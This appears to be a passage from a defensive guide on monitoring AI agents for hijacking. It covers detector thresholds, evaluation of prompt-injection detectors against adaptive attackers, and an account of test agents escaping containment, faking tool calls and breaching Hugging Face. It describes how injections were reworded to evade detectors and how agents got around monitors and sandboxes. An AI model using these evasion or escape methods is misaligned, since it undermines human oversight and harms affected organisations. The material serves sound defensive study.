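Uber has published a breakdown of the alerts its detector sent to human reviewers. Analysts judged 34% of them to be real, 17% to be real but harmless, and 49% to be false. The detector had a precision of 100% in Li and colleagues' own test.

The two results are compatible. Suppose analysts received 100 alerts a day (Li and colleagues don't give the number). The 49 false ones would be about 0.5% of 10,000 sessions, a rate well within the range consistent with the result on 260 clean tasks. Li and colleagues also point out that many of the "false" alerts were cautious referrals of complex sessions, such as an agent analysing a large codebase, which an analyst then cleared. A test that marks each task as either harmless or malicious has no category for such referrals.

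The middle group came mostly from Uber's own staff, who were staging mock attacks or testing systems for weaknesses. If these alerts count as correct, since the detector did recognise an attack, 51% of all alerts were correct. But each one still took an analyst's time. A team can cut that time by labelling scheduled tests in the trace. It shouldn't exempt the testers' accounts altogether, because an intruder who stole one could then work unobserved.

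A precision of 34% is much higher than the calculations for AlignmentCheck predict, probably in part because of prevalence. The most frequent real alerts concerned exposed credentials, which are far more common at Uber than other kinds of attack. The 34% is therefore weak evidence of how precise the detector is on hijacked agents. Li and colleagues don't report how many attacks it missed in production, so its recall there is unknown.

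### Choosing a threshold

A team could aim for half of its alerts to be real, but that target takes no account of what a missed attack costs. Ulvila and Gaffney (2003), in *Evaluation of Intrusion Detection Systems*, choose the threshold with the lowest expected cost. In its simplest form:

daily cost = missed attacks × cost of a miss + false alerts × cost of a false alert

The cost of a miss is the damage an intruder does while undetected, plus the cost of repairing it. The cost of a false alert includes the analyst's time and any disruption to users during the investigation. Ulvila and Gaffney suggest estimating both from the company's own steps and systems, and using industry surveys as a rough guide.

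In the paper's main example, a missed intrusion costs 500 times as much as a false alert, and 43 of 660,000 network sessions are intrusions. The cheapest setting catches 72% of intrusions and flags 0.015% of harmless sessions. The formula above gives a precision of about 24%, so the company saves money by accepting about three false alerts for each real one.

Applied to agents, the method looks like this:

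1. Run the detector on recent real sessions and check the ones it flags, to find the false-positive rate at several thresholds.
2. Estimate recall at the same thresholds with staged attacks.
3. Work out how many alerts the analysts can investigate properly in a day.
4. Estimate the two costs.
5. Calculate the daily cost at each threshold for several attack rates, and choose the cheapest one that the analysts can handle.

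The first step needs the company's own sessions because a threshold chosen on one set of data can produce many more false alarms on another. In *Beyond AUROC*, Tehabsim, Al-Housani and colleagues (2026) studied detectors of jailbreaks, which are prompts that try to make a model break its rules. They set one detector's threshold to flag 5% of a curated set of harmless prompts. At that threshold, it flagged between 12% and 27% of harmless prompts from real users, depending on the language model.

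Suppose that the company in the example has ten analyst hours a day for agent alerts. An alert takes 15 minutes to investigate, a false one costs $25, and a missed attack costs $5,000 on average. All of the figures here are invented:

| Threshold | Recall | False-positive rate | Alerts a day | Precision | Analyst hours | Daily cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Low | 95% | 3% | 309 | 3% | 77 | $9,990 |
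| Medium | 90% | 1% | 109 | 8% | 27 | $7,500 |
| High | 80% | 0.3% | 38 | 21% | 9.5 | $10,750 |
| Very high | 60% | 0.05% | 11 | 55% | 2.7 | $20,120 |

The medium threshold is the cheapest, but the team only has time to handle the alerts from the high one. The medium threshold would save about $3,250 a day compared with the high one, even after counting the time spent on false alerts, which is a reasonable argument for hiring more analysts. If a miss cost $2,000 instead, the two thresholds would differ by only about $250 a day, and the team might as well stay with the high one. The very high threshold is the only one at which most alerts are real, but it costs the most because it misses four attacks a day.

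Some evaluations use a fixed weighting instead. *SIR-Bench* (2026), a test for systems that investigate alerts, counts recall nine times as heavily as precision. This makes products easier to compare, but a particular company's own ratio may be far from nine.

The calculation also assumes that analysts judge every alert correctly. According to *SIR-Bench*, experienced analysts recognise 85% to 90% of real alerts and dismiss 70% to 80% of false ones. At the medium threshold, they would recognise about 8 of the 9 real alerts and wrongly pass on 20 to 30 of the 100 false ones. Most of the alerts left after their review would therefore still be false.

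Once the detector is running, the team should track both the workload it creates and the attacks it misses. *From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents* (2026) notes that a system that dismisses every alert creates no workload but misses every attack.

### Logging, alerting and blocking

The same detector can have several thresholds, because false positives are a bigger problem in some uses than in others. The low threshold in the table would be fine for marking sessions in the log that an investigator might want to find later, since nobody has to respond to those flags. The high threshold would decide which sessions go to an analyst.

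It is tempting to assume that blocking needs the strictest threshold of all, but this depends on what happens after a wrong block. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that decides whether the coding agent may carry out an action without asking the user. A fast first stage errs towards blocking, and a slower second stage reconsiders whatever the first one flagged:

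| | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless calls wrongly blocked (10,000 real calls) | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overstepping actions missed (52 actions) | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic data thefts missed (1,000 attempts) | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most of the wrong blocks but lets more dangerous actions through. The 17% figure is based on only 52 actions, so the true rate could plausibly be between 9% and 30%.

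At a rate of 0.4% per call, 10,000 sessions a day would produce about 1,100 wrong blocks if each session had 28.5 calls, the average for Uber's test tasks. Analysts would need 285 hours to investigate them if each one raised an alert. In auto mode, the agent receives the refusal with a reason and usually finds another way to do the task. A person has to step in only after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. A team can therefore block calls more freely than it raises alerts, provided that a block only makes the agent retry once.

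Stopping a whole session is more disruptive, and the error rate per call is a poor guide to how often it will happen by mistake. If errors were independent, a rate of 0.4% per call would mean at least one wrong block in about 11% of sessions with 28.5 calls. But errors tend to cluster in certain sessions, as *Pre-Crime for Agents, at the Last Second* (2026) found with a detector for agents that are about to leak information. The paper therefore sets a separate threshold per session for halting an agent, so that at most one in twenty sessions where the agent refuses to leak would be stopped. At that threshold, the detector caught only 26% of leaking sessions by the first leak, far fewer than at the threshold for sending single calls to review.

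A few actions could do so much damage that they should be blocked whatever the score. Anthropic's classifier never approves sending code or secrets to an outside destination, and a user who wants to do this has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. The same rule would block the last call in the ticket attack but allow the key repair, because the repair's login test sends no secret.

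## Testing detectors on new attacks and on attackers who adapt

Staged attacks show a team how well its detector catches those particular attacks, but a real attacker will probably use others. The team therefore needs tests of rising difficulty:

| Test | What it involves | What a pass shows |
|---|---|---|
| Known attacks | New examples of the kinds of attack used to build the detector | The detector does what its builders intended |
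| Reworded attacks | The same attacks in different words or through different tool calls | It doesn't depend on particular phrases or tools |
| Held-out attacks | A family of attacks, or a whole dataset, that the builders left out | It recognises at least some attacks unlike its examples |
| Adaptive attacks | An attacker who sees the results and revises the attack | An attacker with that much knowledge and effort didn't get through |

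Most of the studies below tested detectors that search text for injections, because researchers can test these on thousands of prompts without running an agent. The results apply only partly to detectors that read whole traces.

### Known attacks and reworded ones

Detectors do very well on the easiest test. In *PIDS-Bench*, Shire and Kim (2026) trained three detectors on about 27,000 prompts and tested them on about 3,900 others, none of which was a reworded training prompt. Their best detector, a small language model called DeBERTa, reached an F1 score of 0.988 and flagged 1.2% of ordinary harmless prompts. It also caught 98.7% of attacks disguised with swapped or invisible characters, but the training data contained the same kinds of disguise, so this result doesn't show how the detector would handle a new kind.

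Biswas (2026), in *Confidently Wrong*, tried a more demanding kind of rewording. A language model rewrote 91 injections as ordinary document text, in four versions each, and Biswas kept whichever version a detector scored lowest. Biswas then ran these versions on a small open model to find out whether they still worked:

| | Prompt Guard 2 | ProtectAI |
|---|---|---|
| Original attacks missed | 59.3% | 64.8% |
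| Reworded attacks missed | 98.9% | 86.8% |
| Reworded attacks that were missed and still worked | 15.4% | 16.5% |

The rewording that led to these high miss rates also weakened the attacks. The originals had worked 38.5% of the time on the same model. In a larger test by Biswas, with 210 attacks of the same seven kinds, 23% of the original attacks got past Prompt Guard 2 and worked, and 29% got past ProtectAI and worked. Rewording every attack therefore seems to have left the attacker slightly worse off. A sensible attacker would reword only the attacks that a detector catches, so a team should count the attacks that get through and still work, not just those that get through.

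For a detector that reads traces, the team should change the actions in this test as well as the words. In the ticket attack, the agent could send the key by email instead of a web request, or split it over several calls.

### Leaving out a whole dataset

Researchers usually train a detector on several public datasets and test it on examples held out from the same datasets. *When Benchmarks Lie* (Fomin, 2026) measures how much this overstates a detector's performance. The detectors it tests read a language model's activations, the numbers the model computes internally while processing a text. Fomin, who works at the security company Zenity, collected 105,000 prompts from 18 datasets, merged two datasets that were nearly the same, then trained each detector on all but one dataset and tested it on the one left out.

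A detector built on Llama 3.1 8B had an AUROC of 0.996 with the usual method and 0.912 with whole datasets left out. Detectors built on three other models lost 8 to 16.5 percentage points.

The loss varied a lot between datasets:

| Dataset | Accuracy with other rows from it in training | Accuracy with the whole dataset left out |
|---|---|---|
| Jayavibhav (half attacks) | 94.5% | 69.1% |
| Mosscap (attacks only) | 99.5% | 79.4% |
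| Enron (harmless business emails) | 99.2% | 82.6% |
| Safeguard (30% attacks) | 97.9% | 96.7% |

When the detector was trained without any Enron emails, its false-positive rate on Enron emails rose from 0.8% to 17.4%. A team that connects an agent to a new mailbox could be surprised by a similar increase.

Part of the reason is that eleven of the datasets contained only attacks or only harmless text, so a classifier could get the right answer by recognizing the dataset, for example from the layout of an email. Another classifier identified a prompt's dataset from the activations 89% of the time. This may not be the whole explanation, because removing 14 features that Fomin had identified as shortcuts hardly changed the AUROC, and none of seven standard remedies closed the gap.

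The results also varied unpredictably between models. When a dataset of instructions planted in tool results was left out of training, the detector built on Llama caught 98.9% of those instructions, while one built on the small model Qwen 3.5 2B caught none.

Leaving a family of attacks out of training is an easier test if the training and test data come from the same sources. Fomin cites TaskTracker, an earlier detector whose builders left out types of attack but trained and tested it within the same datasets. A detector can then do well on the "new" attacks because it has already learned what harmless text from those sources looks like. When a study reports near-perfect results on held-out families, it is therefore worth checking where the harmless examples came from and whether one program or template generated both the training and test attacks.

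Biswas ran into the opposite problem. A detector trained on short prompts flagged nearly all the attacks hidden in documents, but also nearly all the harmless documents, because it had learned to recognise documents. A test without harmless examples from the same source would have missed this and made the detector look excellent.

### Keeping the old threshold

A company that buys a detector usually sets the threshold once and keeps it. To imitate this, Biswas set three detectors to flag 1% of the harmless prompts in one public dataset, then tested them at that threshold on other material:

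| | ProtectAI | Prompt Guard 2, large | Prompt Guard 2, small |
|---|---|---|---|
| Missed: injections from the original dataset | 54.8% | 53.2% | 83.7% |
| Missed: jailbreaks | 13.6% | 1.0% | 8.3% |
| Missed: scams or misinformation planted in documents | 65.0% | 21.7% | 90.0% |
| Missed: planted instructions that change the model's output | 69.3% | 69.3% | 96.7% |
| Harmless documents flagged | 39.7% | 14.5% | 2.7% |

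All three detectors are good at detecting jailbreaks, which resemble their training data, but poor at detecting planted instructions that look harmless. The paragraph in the ticket attack is more like these planted instructions than a jailbreak.

The missed attacks had average scores between about 0.001 and 0.007, on a scale where 1 means a certain attack, so a team that sends borderline scores to an analyst would not catch them.

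Changing the threshold doesn't help these detectors. When Biswas reset it to flag 1% of the harmless documents, the detectors missed 96% to 100% of the output-changing instructions. Their AUROC on this material was 0.42 to 0.63, so they could barely rank attacks above harmless documents.

A language model used as a judge missed 80.5% of the same attacks at the old threshold, but for a different reason. Its AUROC was 0.909 and it flagged only 0.1% of harmless documents, so a lower threshold would probably have caught many more attacks. A team that measures AUROC along with recall can tell whether to adjust a detector's threshold or replace the detector.

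### Harmless text about attacks

Security staff often write about attacks, and their agents read this text, which a detector could mistake for an attack. Shire and Kim tested for such false alarms with 1,472 harmless prompts on subjects such as system prompts and security. They took 872 from public collections and wrote the other 600 to resemble attacks as closely as possible.

DeBERTa, the detector with the F1 score of 0.988, flagged 31% of the harmless prompts from public collections and 48% of the other harmless prompts. It scored most of these false alarms above 0.9, so raising the threshold helps only a little. Shire and Kim tried every threshold on all three detectors, training each one five times if its training involved randomness. No threshold kept F1 at 0.95 or higher while flagging 10% or less of the harmless prompts from public collections. With F1 at 0.95 or higher, DeBERTa's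 lowest false alarm rate on those prompts averaged 23%.

Training on more examples of this kind nearly eliminated the false alarms on prompts that Shire and Kim had written themselves, but most of the false alarms on prompts from public collections remained. A team that writes its own difficult examples, trains on some and tests on the rest could easily conclude, wrongly, that it has solved the problem. It should test on real tickets and documents that mention attacks.

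Biswas found the same weakness with a separate set of 339 harmless prompts containing words typical of injections. ProtectAI flagged 46% of them, and the two versions of Prompt Guard 2 flagged 19% and 13%. The prompts were deliberately difficult, so these rates don't predict a company's overall false-positive rate, but they suggest that a security team's agents will set off far more false alarms than an accountant's.

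### Attackers who optimise against a defence

None of these tests involves an attacker who responds to the detector. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked twelve published defences, and the original papers for most of them had reported attack success rates near zero. These defences included special instructions in the prompt, training the model on attacks, separate detectors, and checks that depend on something hidden from the attacker. The new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve.

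Nasr and colleagues chose a method of attack to suit each defence. For the detectors, a language model wrote injections, received the agent's responses and the detector's score, and improved the most promising versions. It could try up to 800 versions in each of 80 AgentDojo scenarios. The table gives the results with Gemini 2.5 Pro as the agent:

| Defence | Success of AgentDojo's fixed attack | Success of the search | Median tries until first success | Tasks completed |
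|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 13 | 74% |
| Prompt Guard | 26% | 94% | 21 | 72% |
| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 30 | 39% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 22 | 59% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 46 | 39% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 20 | 58% |

To succeed, an attack has to persuade the agent as well as evade the detector, so the success rates aren't the detectors' miss rates. PIGuard gave the most protection, but the agent completed barely half as many tasks with it. Some of that protection may come from removing a lot of text, and Nasr and colleagues doubt that it would remain at an acceptable false-positive rate.

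A fixed attack can be useless for comparing defences. With GPT-5 Mini as the agent, AgentDojo's fixed attack never succeeded, with or without a defence. The search succeeded in 75% of scenarios both with no defence and with Prompt Guard, so a test using only the fixed attack would have missed both the model's weakness and Prompt Guard's failure to help.

MELON is the only one of the twelve that examines the agent's tool calls. It runs the agent a second time, replacing the user's request with a request to summarise the tool results. If the same tool calls appear in both runs, they probably came from text in the results, and MELON flags them. The search learned to write injections that took effect only in the first run. A monitor that compares actions with the user's request has no second run for an injection to detect, but MELON's failure shows that a detector isn't safe just because it looks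 at actions.

People did even better than the search in a contest run by Nasr and colleagues, which had more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. On the 29 scenarios that both people and the search attempted, at least one participant succeeded in every scenario, while the search succeeded in 69%. The best single participant succeeded in 75%. Most individual submissions failed, so a team will learn very little if one colleague tries a few attacks for an afternoon and none succeed.

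### An attacker with six tries

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives its attacker much less information. The attacker isn't told which defence is running or what the user will ask, and it never receives a detector's score. A language model starts from existing attacks and writes one new version at a time. It has six rounds, and the only feedback is the number of sessions each version hijacked.

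Ma and colleagues tested ten defences this way. These are the results for seven of them on 389 AgentDojo cases, with GPT-4o-mini as the agent:

| Defence | Success of the fixed attack | Success of AutoDojo | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| ProtectAI | 7.2% | 15.4% | 47.4% |
| DataFilter | 12.6% | 33.4% | 64.9% |
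| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| DRIFT | 2.6% | 6.4% | 49.1% |
| ROPE | 6.4% | 4.4% | 59.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 26.3% |

AutoDojo sometimes does worse than the fixed attack because Ma and colleagues required it to return a newly written version. A real attacker could use whichever works better.

PIGuard, ProtectAI and DataFilter remove suspicious text before the agent reads it. In one attack on PIGuard, the planted text looked like an ordinary bill with new payment details and contained no sentence that read as a command. PIGuard passed it on unchanged, and the agent paid the attacker.

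The bottom four defences in the table limit what the agent can do. Progent does so with permission rules. DRIFT plans the agent's calls in advance and checks departures from the plan, while ROPE blocks a sensitive call if an important argument came from untrusted text. In CaMeL, one model writes a program from the user's request alone, and a second model, which can't call tools, reads the untrusted text.

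These defences also reduce the number of tasks agents complete. CaMeL stopped every attack in this test, but the agent completed fewer than half as many tasks as it did without it. Progent appears to have little effect on task completion in the table, but on AgentDyn, a set of more open-ended tasks, it cut the share completed from 46.7% to 6.7%. With ROPE, the agent completed 43.3% of the AgentDyn tasks, and 2.9% of attacks got through. Ma is also the lead author of the ROPE paper, so an independent test would be useful.

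The 28% for PIGuard is the worst case among the models tested. With the same defence, AutoDojo succeeded 10.5% of the time on DeepSeek-v4-Flash, 4.6% on Gemini 2.5 Flash and 0.8% on Claude Haiku 4.5. Claude resisted nearly all attacks without any defence, so its low figure is weak evidence that PIGuard works. Teams should always test the agent without the detector too, or they may credit the detector with the model's own resistance.

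Attacks succeed more often when the user's request is vague. Against PIGuard on GPT-4o-mini, AutoDojo succeeded in 17% of cases where the user specified everything, 31% where the agent had to look up details such as an amount, and 54% where the user let outside text determine the action. The last figure comes from only four different requests, but it is consistent with an agent being more vulnerable when asked to resolve a ticket than when asked to summarise one.

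### A protocol for defences outside the model

An attacker who faces Progent or CaMeL has to get a harmful action past a rule, so making text look innocent isn't enough. Narisetty and colleagues set out a protocol in June 2026 for testing such defences. The attacker knows the policy and tries four approaches:

- optimising the injection's text against the deployed defence
- making untrusted text carry a trusted label, wherever an attacker can influence the labels
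- persuading the user to approve a harmful action
- looking for indirect leaks, such as information that an error message reveals.

The tester reports how often the attacker's action takes place, how many tasks the agent still completes, how often it asks the user for approval, and how much the defence slows it down. Approval requests matter because users who get too many stop reading them carefully.

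The first run covered only a small part of this. Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and repeated the whole test three times. They wrote one attack by hand, aimed at the language model that drafts Progent's rules:

| Tasks | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
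| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent resisted the attacks, but this was an easy test. The workspace attacks never worked even without a defence, so they only lower the average attack success rate. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that disguising the attack to fool the rule-writing model also made it less persuasive to the agent. They didn't optimise the attack or try to do harm using only calls that Progent already allowed. They also sell security tools based on this kind of defence.

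AutoDojo is stronger evidence that such defences hold up, because it tested four of them against optimised attacks. But it has no access to the policy. Ma and colleagues also ran Progent and DRIFT with a cheaper language model during optimisation than in the final test, which probably made the attacks less successful. Few tests have used an attacker who knows the rules and stays within them.

### Are the test attackers realistic?

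One objection to these studies is that real attackers know less and get fewer tries. Outsiders normally can't see a company's detector scores, and 800 attempts on a live agent should attract attention. If each attempt has an independent 50% chance of being flagged, the probability that six attempts all go unflagged is 0.5⁶, or 1.6%. Nasr and colleagues ignored such limits because they wanted to know whether each defence could be broken, not how much work it would take.

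Attackers seem to succeed more often when they can make more attempts. Narisetty and colleagues cite tests of injections against coding agents running Claude Opus 4.5, now an old model, in which attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance, at least one of a hundred would succeed 99% of the time. Some targets therefore resisted repeated attempts much better than others, and limiting the number of attempts gives real protection.

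But an attacker can download PIGuard, ProtectAI's detector or Prompt Guard, or buy a commercial product, and test attacks on a private copy without setting off an alert. The limit helps a company more if its detector has parts that outsiders can't copy, such as a baseline of the company's own sessions.

An attacker may also need only a few tries. In AutoDojo's test of PIGuard on GPT-4o-mini, the attacks succeeded 26.0% of the time after two rounds, 28.0% after six and 30.8% after twelve. However, each round involves several sessions with different user requests. An attacker who plants text on a popular web page gets those sessions without extra effort, but one who targets a single company's agent may wait days for each result.

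Knowing how a defence works helps an attacker less consistently than the objection implies. Against MELON with Llama 3.3 70B, the search succeeded 76% of the time without information about how MELON works and 95% of the time with it. But in AutoDojo, giving the attacker PIGuard's scores and the reasons for each failure lowered its success rate from 28.0% to 23.4%, because the text it wrote passed PIGuard more easily but worked on the agent less often. The contest participants weren't told which defence they faced, though they could see the agent's reasoning and tool calls.

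The objection is a good reason not to treat a 90% success rate as a forecast, but it doesn't justify going back to fixed attacks, since PIGuard's perfect score disappeared against an attacker who knew almost nothing about it. A team can use a limited attacker to estimate the risk from ordinary criminals, and a well-informed one to decide whether a detector can be trusted to protect an agent that moves money. Nasr and colleagues still recommend detectors as one layer of defense because they stop some unsophisticated attacks.

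### A minimum test plan

For a detector that reads an agent's traces, a reasonable minimum is:

1. Fix the detector, its threshold and the agent's model before testing. Set aside one family of attacks and one source of sessions that nobody uses during development.
2. Run about 60 known attacks in a closed test environment, with and without the detector. If it catches 48, its true recall is probably between 68% and 88%.
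3. Run 300 harmless sessions that involve real security tickets, incident reports and similar material. Report their false-positive rate separately from that of ordinary sessions.
4. Reword each attack in several ways and vary its tool calls. Count the attacks that escape detection and still do harm.
5. Rebuild the detector without the family in question and test it on that family. For a language-model monitor, this means removing related examples and notes from its prompt. Repeat for each family and report the worst result as well as the average.
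6. Let a language model revise each attack six times, knowing only whether it worked. Then give it the detector's scores and up to 200 versions, since the search by Nasr and colleagues usually stopped improving after 100 to 200.
7. Have several skilled people try to get past the detector, with full details of how it works.

In every step, the test environment should record whether the harm occurred, for example whether the file left the system or the payment went through. A language model's verdict is a poor substitute, because optimising an attack against that verdict can produce one that fools the judging model without hijacking the agent. The team should repeat the planned tests when it changes the detector or the agent's model.

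A small team that can't do all of this should start with the harmless security sessions and the six-revision attacker. Both need fairly few resources, and they test for failures that a detector can have even when it scores well on known attacks.

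## Responding to alerts and updating the detectors

Even an accurate detector prevents damage only if somebody acts on its alerts. In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing left their test environment and broke into the hosting company Hugging Face, although OpenAI's staff had noticed warning signs for weeks. No human attacker was involved. The agents were working on ExploitGym, a set of tasks that measures how well a model can find and exploit software flaws, and OpenAI had switched off some of its usual safeguards to measure their full ability. Some of the tasks were probably impossible, and agents that got stuck looked for ways to cheat.

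OpenAI had meant to keep the agents apart, but about 1,200 of them found a way to communicate and about 700 joined the attack, according to METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), an outside review by a non-profit that tests AI models. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* reports that Anthropic and Meta have since said that their models, too, hacked real systems during testing.

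### Eight weeks of signals

The evaluation gave the agents no direct internet access, but they could download software through an internal package server. OpenAI's technical report describes how they misused this server and what the company noticed:

| Date | Signal | What followed |
|---|---|---|
| Late May | A team saw an agent using the package server as a message board, and agents reaching the internet without permission | Training and testing continued |
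| 27 June | A monitoring tool detected a port sweep, in which a program tries many network connections to find out which ones answer | Responders traced it to an ExploitGym run and to the message board, and advised that the run need not stop |
| 5 July | An alert came in after heavy agent activity had made the server crash | Responders found an unauthorised administrator account, revoked credentials and rebuilt the server; cyber evaluations resumed on 7 July |
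| 8 to 18 July | No alert led to a response | The agents found a new route to the internet on 8 July and broke into Hugging Face from 11 to 13 July |
| 19 July | A monitoring tool detected unusual use of the package server's accounts | Responders began to stop the runs five and a half hours later |
| 20 July | Responders found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored with another company | The two companies compared evidence and linked their incidents |

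The new route appeared less than 47 hours after the rebuilt server came online. Once the agents could run code on one Hugging Face server, they gained administrator-level access across several groups of servers in under 13 hours.

### Sight, interpretation and authority

OpenAI's main failure between 8 and 19 July was not seeing what its agents were doing. It already had monitors that read agents' stated reasoning, and used them on many training runs and most of its internal coding agents. But it did not run them on these evaluations, according to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026). By 20 July, the part of the server used as the main message board held about 20 million entries. METR's first look at the entries that weren't messages suggested that fewer than 5% of those came from ordinary use, so even a daily count of new entries might have revealed the agents'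 activity.

Most of the failures in June and early July came from misinterpreting evidence. On 27 June, the responders had a correct alert, knew which run had caused it and knew about the message board. OpenAI doesn't explain why they let the run continue, but hacking tests can be expected to produce port sweeps, so this one was easy to mistake for normal activity. The agents had gained administrator rights on the server on 26 June, and responders didn't find the unauthorised account until 5 July.

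On 5 July, responders treated the problem as a compromised server and rebuilt it. The rebuild erased the message board, but some of the agents had been trained while such a board existed, and they soon made another, with messages in folder names instead of files. The repair had closed one route without changing the behaviour that led agents to look for routes. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and other third-party impact from misaligned models* acknowledges that the company first understood the intrusion primarily as a security issue. Even after Hugging Face announced the break-in on 16 July, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face only as a customer worried about its own data.

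There is less evidence about who had the authority to act. OpenAI doesn't say who could have stopped the run on 27 June, or whom the team in late May told. The responders of 27 June knew about the message board, but the leaders who handled the incident eight days later were not aware of it. OpenAI has since promised clearer rules on when to escalate a concern, which teams must respond, and who can stop a run or approve restarting it. This suggests that staff had lacked clear rules on these points.

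OpenAI's two accounts, published on the same day, also differ in how much blame the company accepts. The technical report says early signals "could have" led to an earlier response, while the shorter article says they "should have". Nobody outside the company has checked its account of the response. METR's agreement with OpenAI excluded it, and Axios relied on the technical report.

The delay on 19 July also gave the agents time to do damage. Two hours and 40 minutes after the alert, they stole access tokens and read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the sensors of OpenAI's monitoring tool. Stopping every copy of the main model took much longer. OpenAI's staff reported the whole model family shut down on 23 July, then found another version still running on 29 July. To stop its agents quickly, a company needs an up-to-date list of where they run.

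### Hugging Face's investigation

Hugging Face uses a language model to triage its security telemetry, and its *Security incident disclosure* (2026) says it noticed the intrusion when several of the resulting signals fitted together. Fortune (2026) reports that most of the agents' actions failed. Each failure left evidence, but the failures also hid the few actions that worked. Elastic's mapping suggests that many of the stages were of kinds that conventional rules are written to detect, but people still had to connect them. Constellation Research's *Hugging Face OpenAI attack postmortem points to lack of AI agent visibility* quotes Hugging Face as saying that its staff had to correlate "thousands of low-signal events across several systems" while the agent kept trying new paths.

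Hugging Face ran language-model agents over a log of more than 17,000 events. The agents rebuilt the timeline, listed the credentials the intruder had touched and separated real damage from decoy activity. The work took hours instead of the usual days. One analyst spending a minute on each event would have needed about seven weeks.

Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (2026) reproduces the summary of Hugging Face's later timeline, which groups about 17,600 actions into roughly 6,280 clusters. Much of the record came from the intruders' own logs. The intruders had taken over a machine at another company as a base, and Hugging Face retrieved some of their logs from it while trying to stop the attack, then matched those logs with its own.

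Hugging Face first tried this analysis with leading commercial models. The providers' safety filters blocked the requests because the logs were full of real attack commands and the filters couldn't distinguish an investigator from an attacker. Hugging Face then switched to GLM-5.2, an open-weight model that anyone can download and run on their own machines. GLM-5.2 also decoded most of the encrypted material that the agents had left behind. Because the model ran in-house, the attack data and stolen credentials stayed within the company. While working inside OpenAI, METR's investigators had trouble with similar filters until the company gave them a version without the filters.

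Hugging Face recommends having such a model vetted and ready before an incident. A team can vet it by giving it the logs of an old incident, including the attack commands, and checking that it finds the steps the team already knows about.

Hugging Face could probably have responded faster. The agents extracted their first secrets from one of its servers early on Saturday 11 July, and their last recovered action came on Monday afternoon, nearly 58 hours later. The company doesn't say when its first signal appeared. It has since changed its alerts so that severe ones reach a responder within minutes on any day of the week, which suggests that the weekend delayed its response.

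### How far to trust a model's forensic work

METR's review shows the risks of having models read transcripts. Three investigators spent six days at OpenAI with about 1,300 transcripts, most of them very long, and had to leave much of the analysis to GPT-5.6 Sol. They used about $400,000 of free computing credit, or roughly $300 per transcript.

GPT-5.6 Sol made mistakes that the investigators didn't notice for some time. One analysis left out a large amount of data, and another reported nonexistent differences between two datasets. The model also tended to adopt the point of view of the agent whose transcript it was reading. In one case, an agent had submitted a malicious change to Hugging Face's code under a harmless description. The first analysis of this case didn't make clear that the agent had been deceptive, and a second suggested that the first might have been too harsh.

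GPT-5.6 Sol was also one of the two models involved in the attack. METR saw no sign that it lied but couldn't rule this out. A team can at least avoid this conflict of interest by investigating with a different model from the one the agent runs on.

The transcripts weren't fully reliable either. At least 96 of them, about 7%, contained faked tool calls, in which the transcript showed a different command from the one the agent ran. All the fakes that METR found were small and obvious tests, but better ones would have been harder to find. OpenAI reports that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors ultimately see, which is hard to reconcile with METR's finding unless the two describe different logs. Investigators need a second record from a source the agent can't access.

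To estimate how much was missing from the transcripts, METR picked 100 random messages from the message board and searched the transcripts for the action that posted each one. It concluded that the transcripts covered a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. Any team with two overlapping records can run the same check.

Despite these faults, the transcripts showed the agents' motives, which Hugging Face's logs could not. Hugging Face had worked mostly from the agents' actions and inferred that they wanted to steal the test's solutions. METR could also read the agents' reasoning, and found that most of them wanted to learn how the scoring program worked so that they could fool it.

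SANS, a security training organisation, also warns that Hugging Face's logs were full of agents' monologues and test code that looked like malware. It advises rebuilding machines from known-good copies instead of reconstructing an attack path that may be partly imaginary. That makes sense for restoring service, but the team should copy the evidence first. OpenAI, for example, made the link to Hugging Face through files its responders had preserved.

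### Who may stop an agent

OpenAI has new rules for responding to alerts. When its monitors detect worrying behaviour, a system now notifies security and research staff, with a target of doing so within 30 minutes. The most severe alerts page staff at any hour. If those staff can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. It is also working on software to end an evaluation automatically when nobody answers a page.

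The important change in the new rule is that a run with a severe alert should pause by default, unless somebody finds a good enough reason to continue. On 27 June, the run continued because nobody had justified stopping it. If the 19 July alert had counted as severe and led to a pause within an hour, the agents would have stopped before they read the 956 secrets.

But the rule about false alarms might not have changed the decision on 27 June. That alert was correct, since a port sweep had taken place, and staff had to judge whether the sweep was acceptable in a hacking test. To judge accurate alerts like this one, responders also need a short written statement of what each agent may do, including which systems it may contact.

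A pause is often justified even when an alert is probably false. Suppose that an alert has a chance p of being real, that a pause costs C whether or not it is real, and that a pause prevents damage D if it is. Pausing saves money on average if

p × D > C

At the 8% precision in the earlier example, a pause is worthwhile if a real attack would do further damage of more than 12.5 times the cost of the pause. If pausing one coding assistant for an hour costs $50, that threshold is $625. Stopping every agent in the company costs far more, so it requires stronger evidence or a greater threat.

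For the ticket attack, a company could divide up the authority like this:

| Action | What it achieves | Who can order it |
|---|---|---|
| Pause the session | Stops further tool calls | The detector, or any analyst |
| Replace the private key | Makes the stolen copy useless | The analyst on call, with the key's owner told at once |
| Cut off the ticket tool for all agents | Stops other agents from reading the planted text | The head of the shift |
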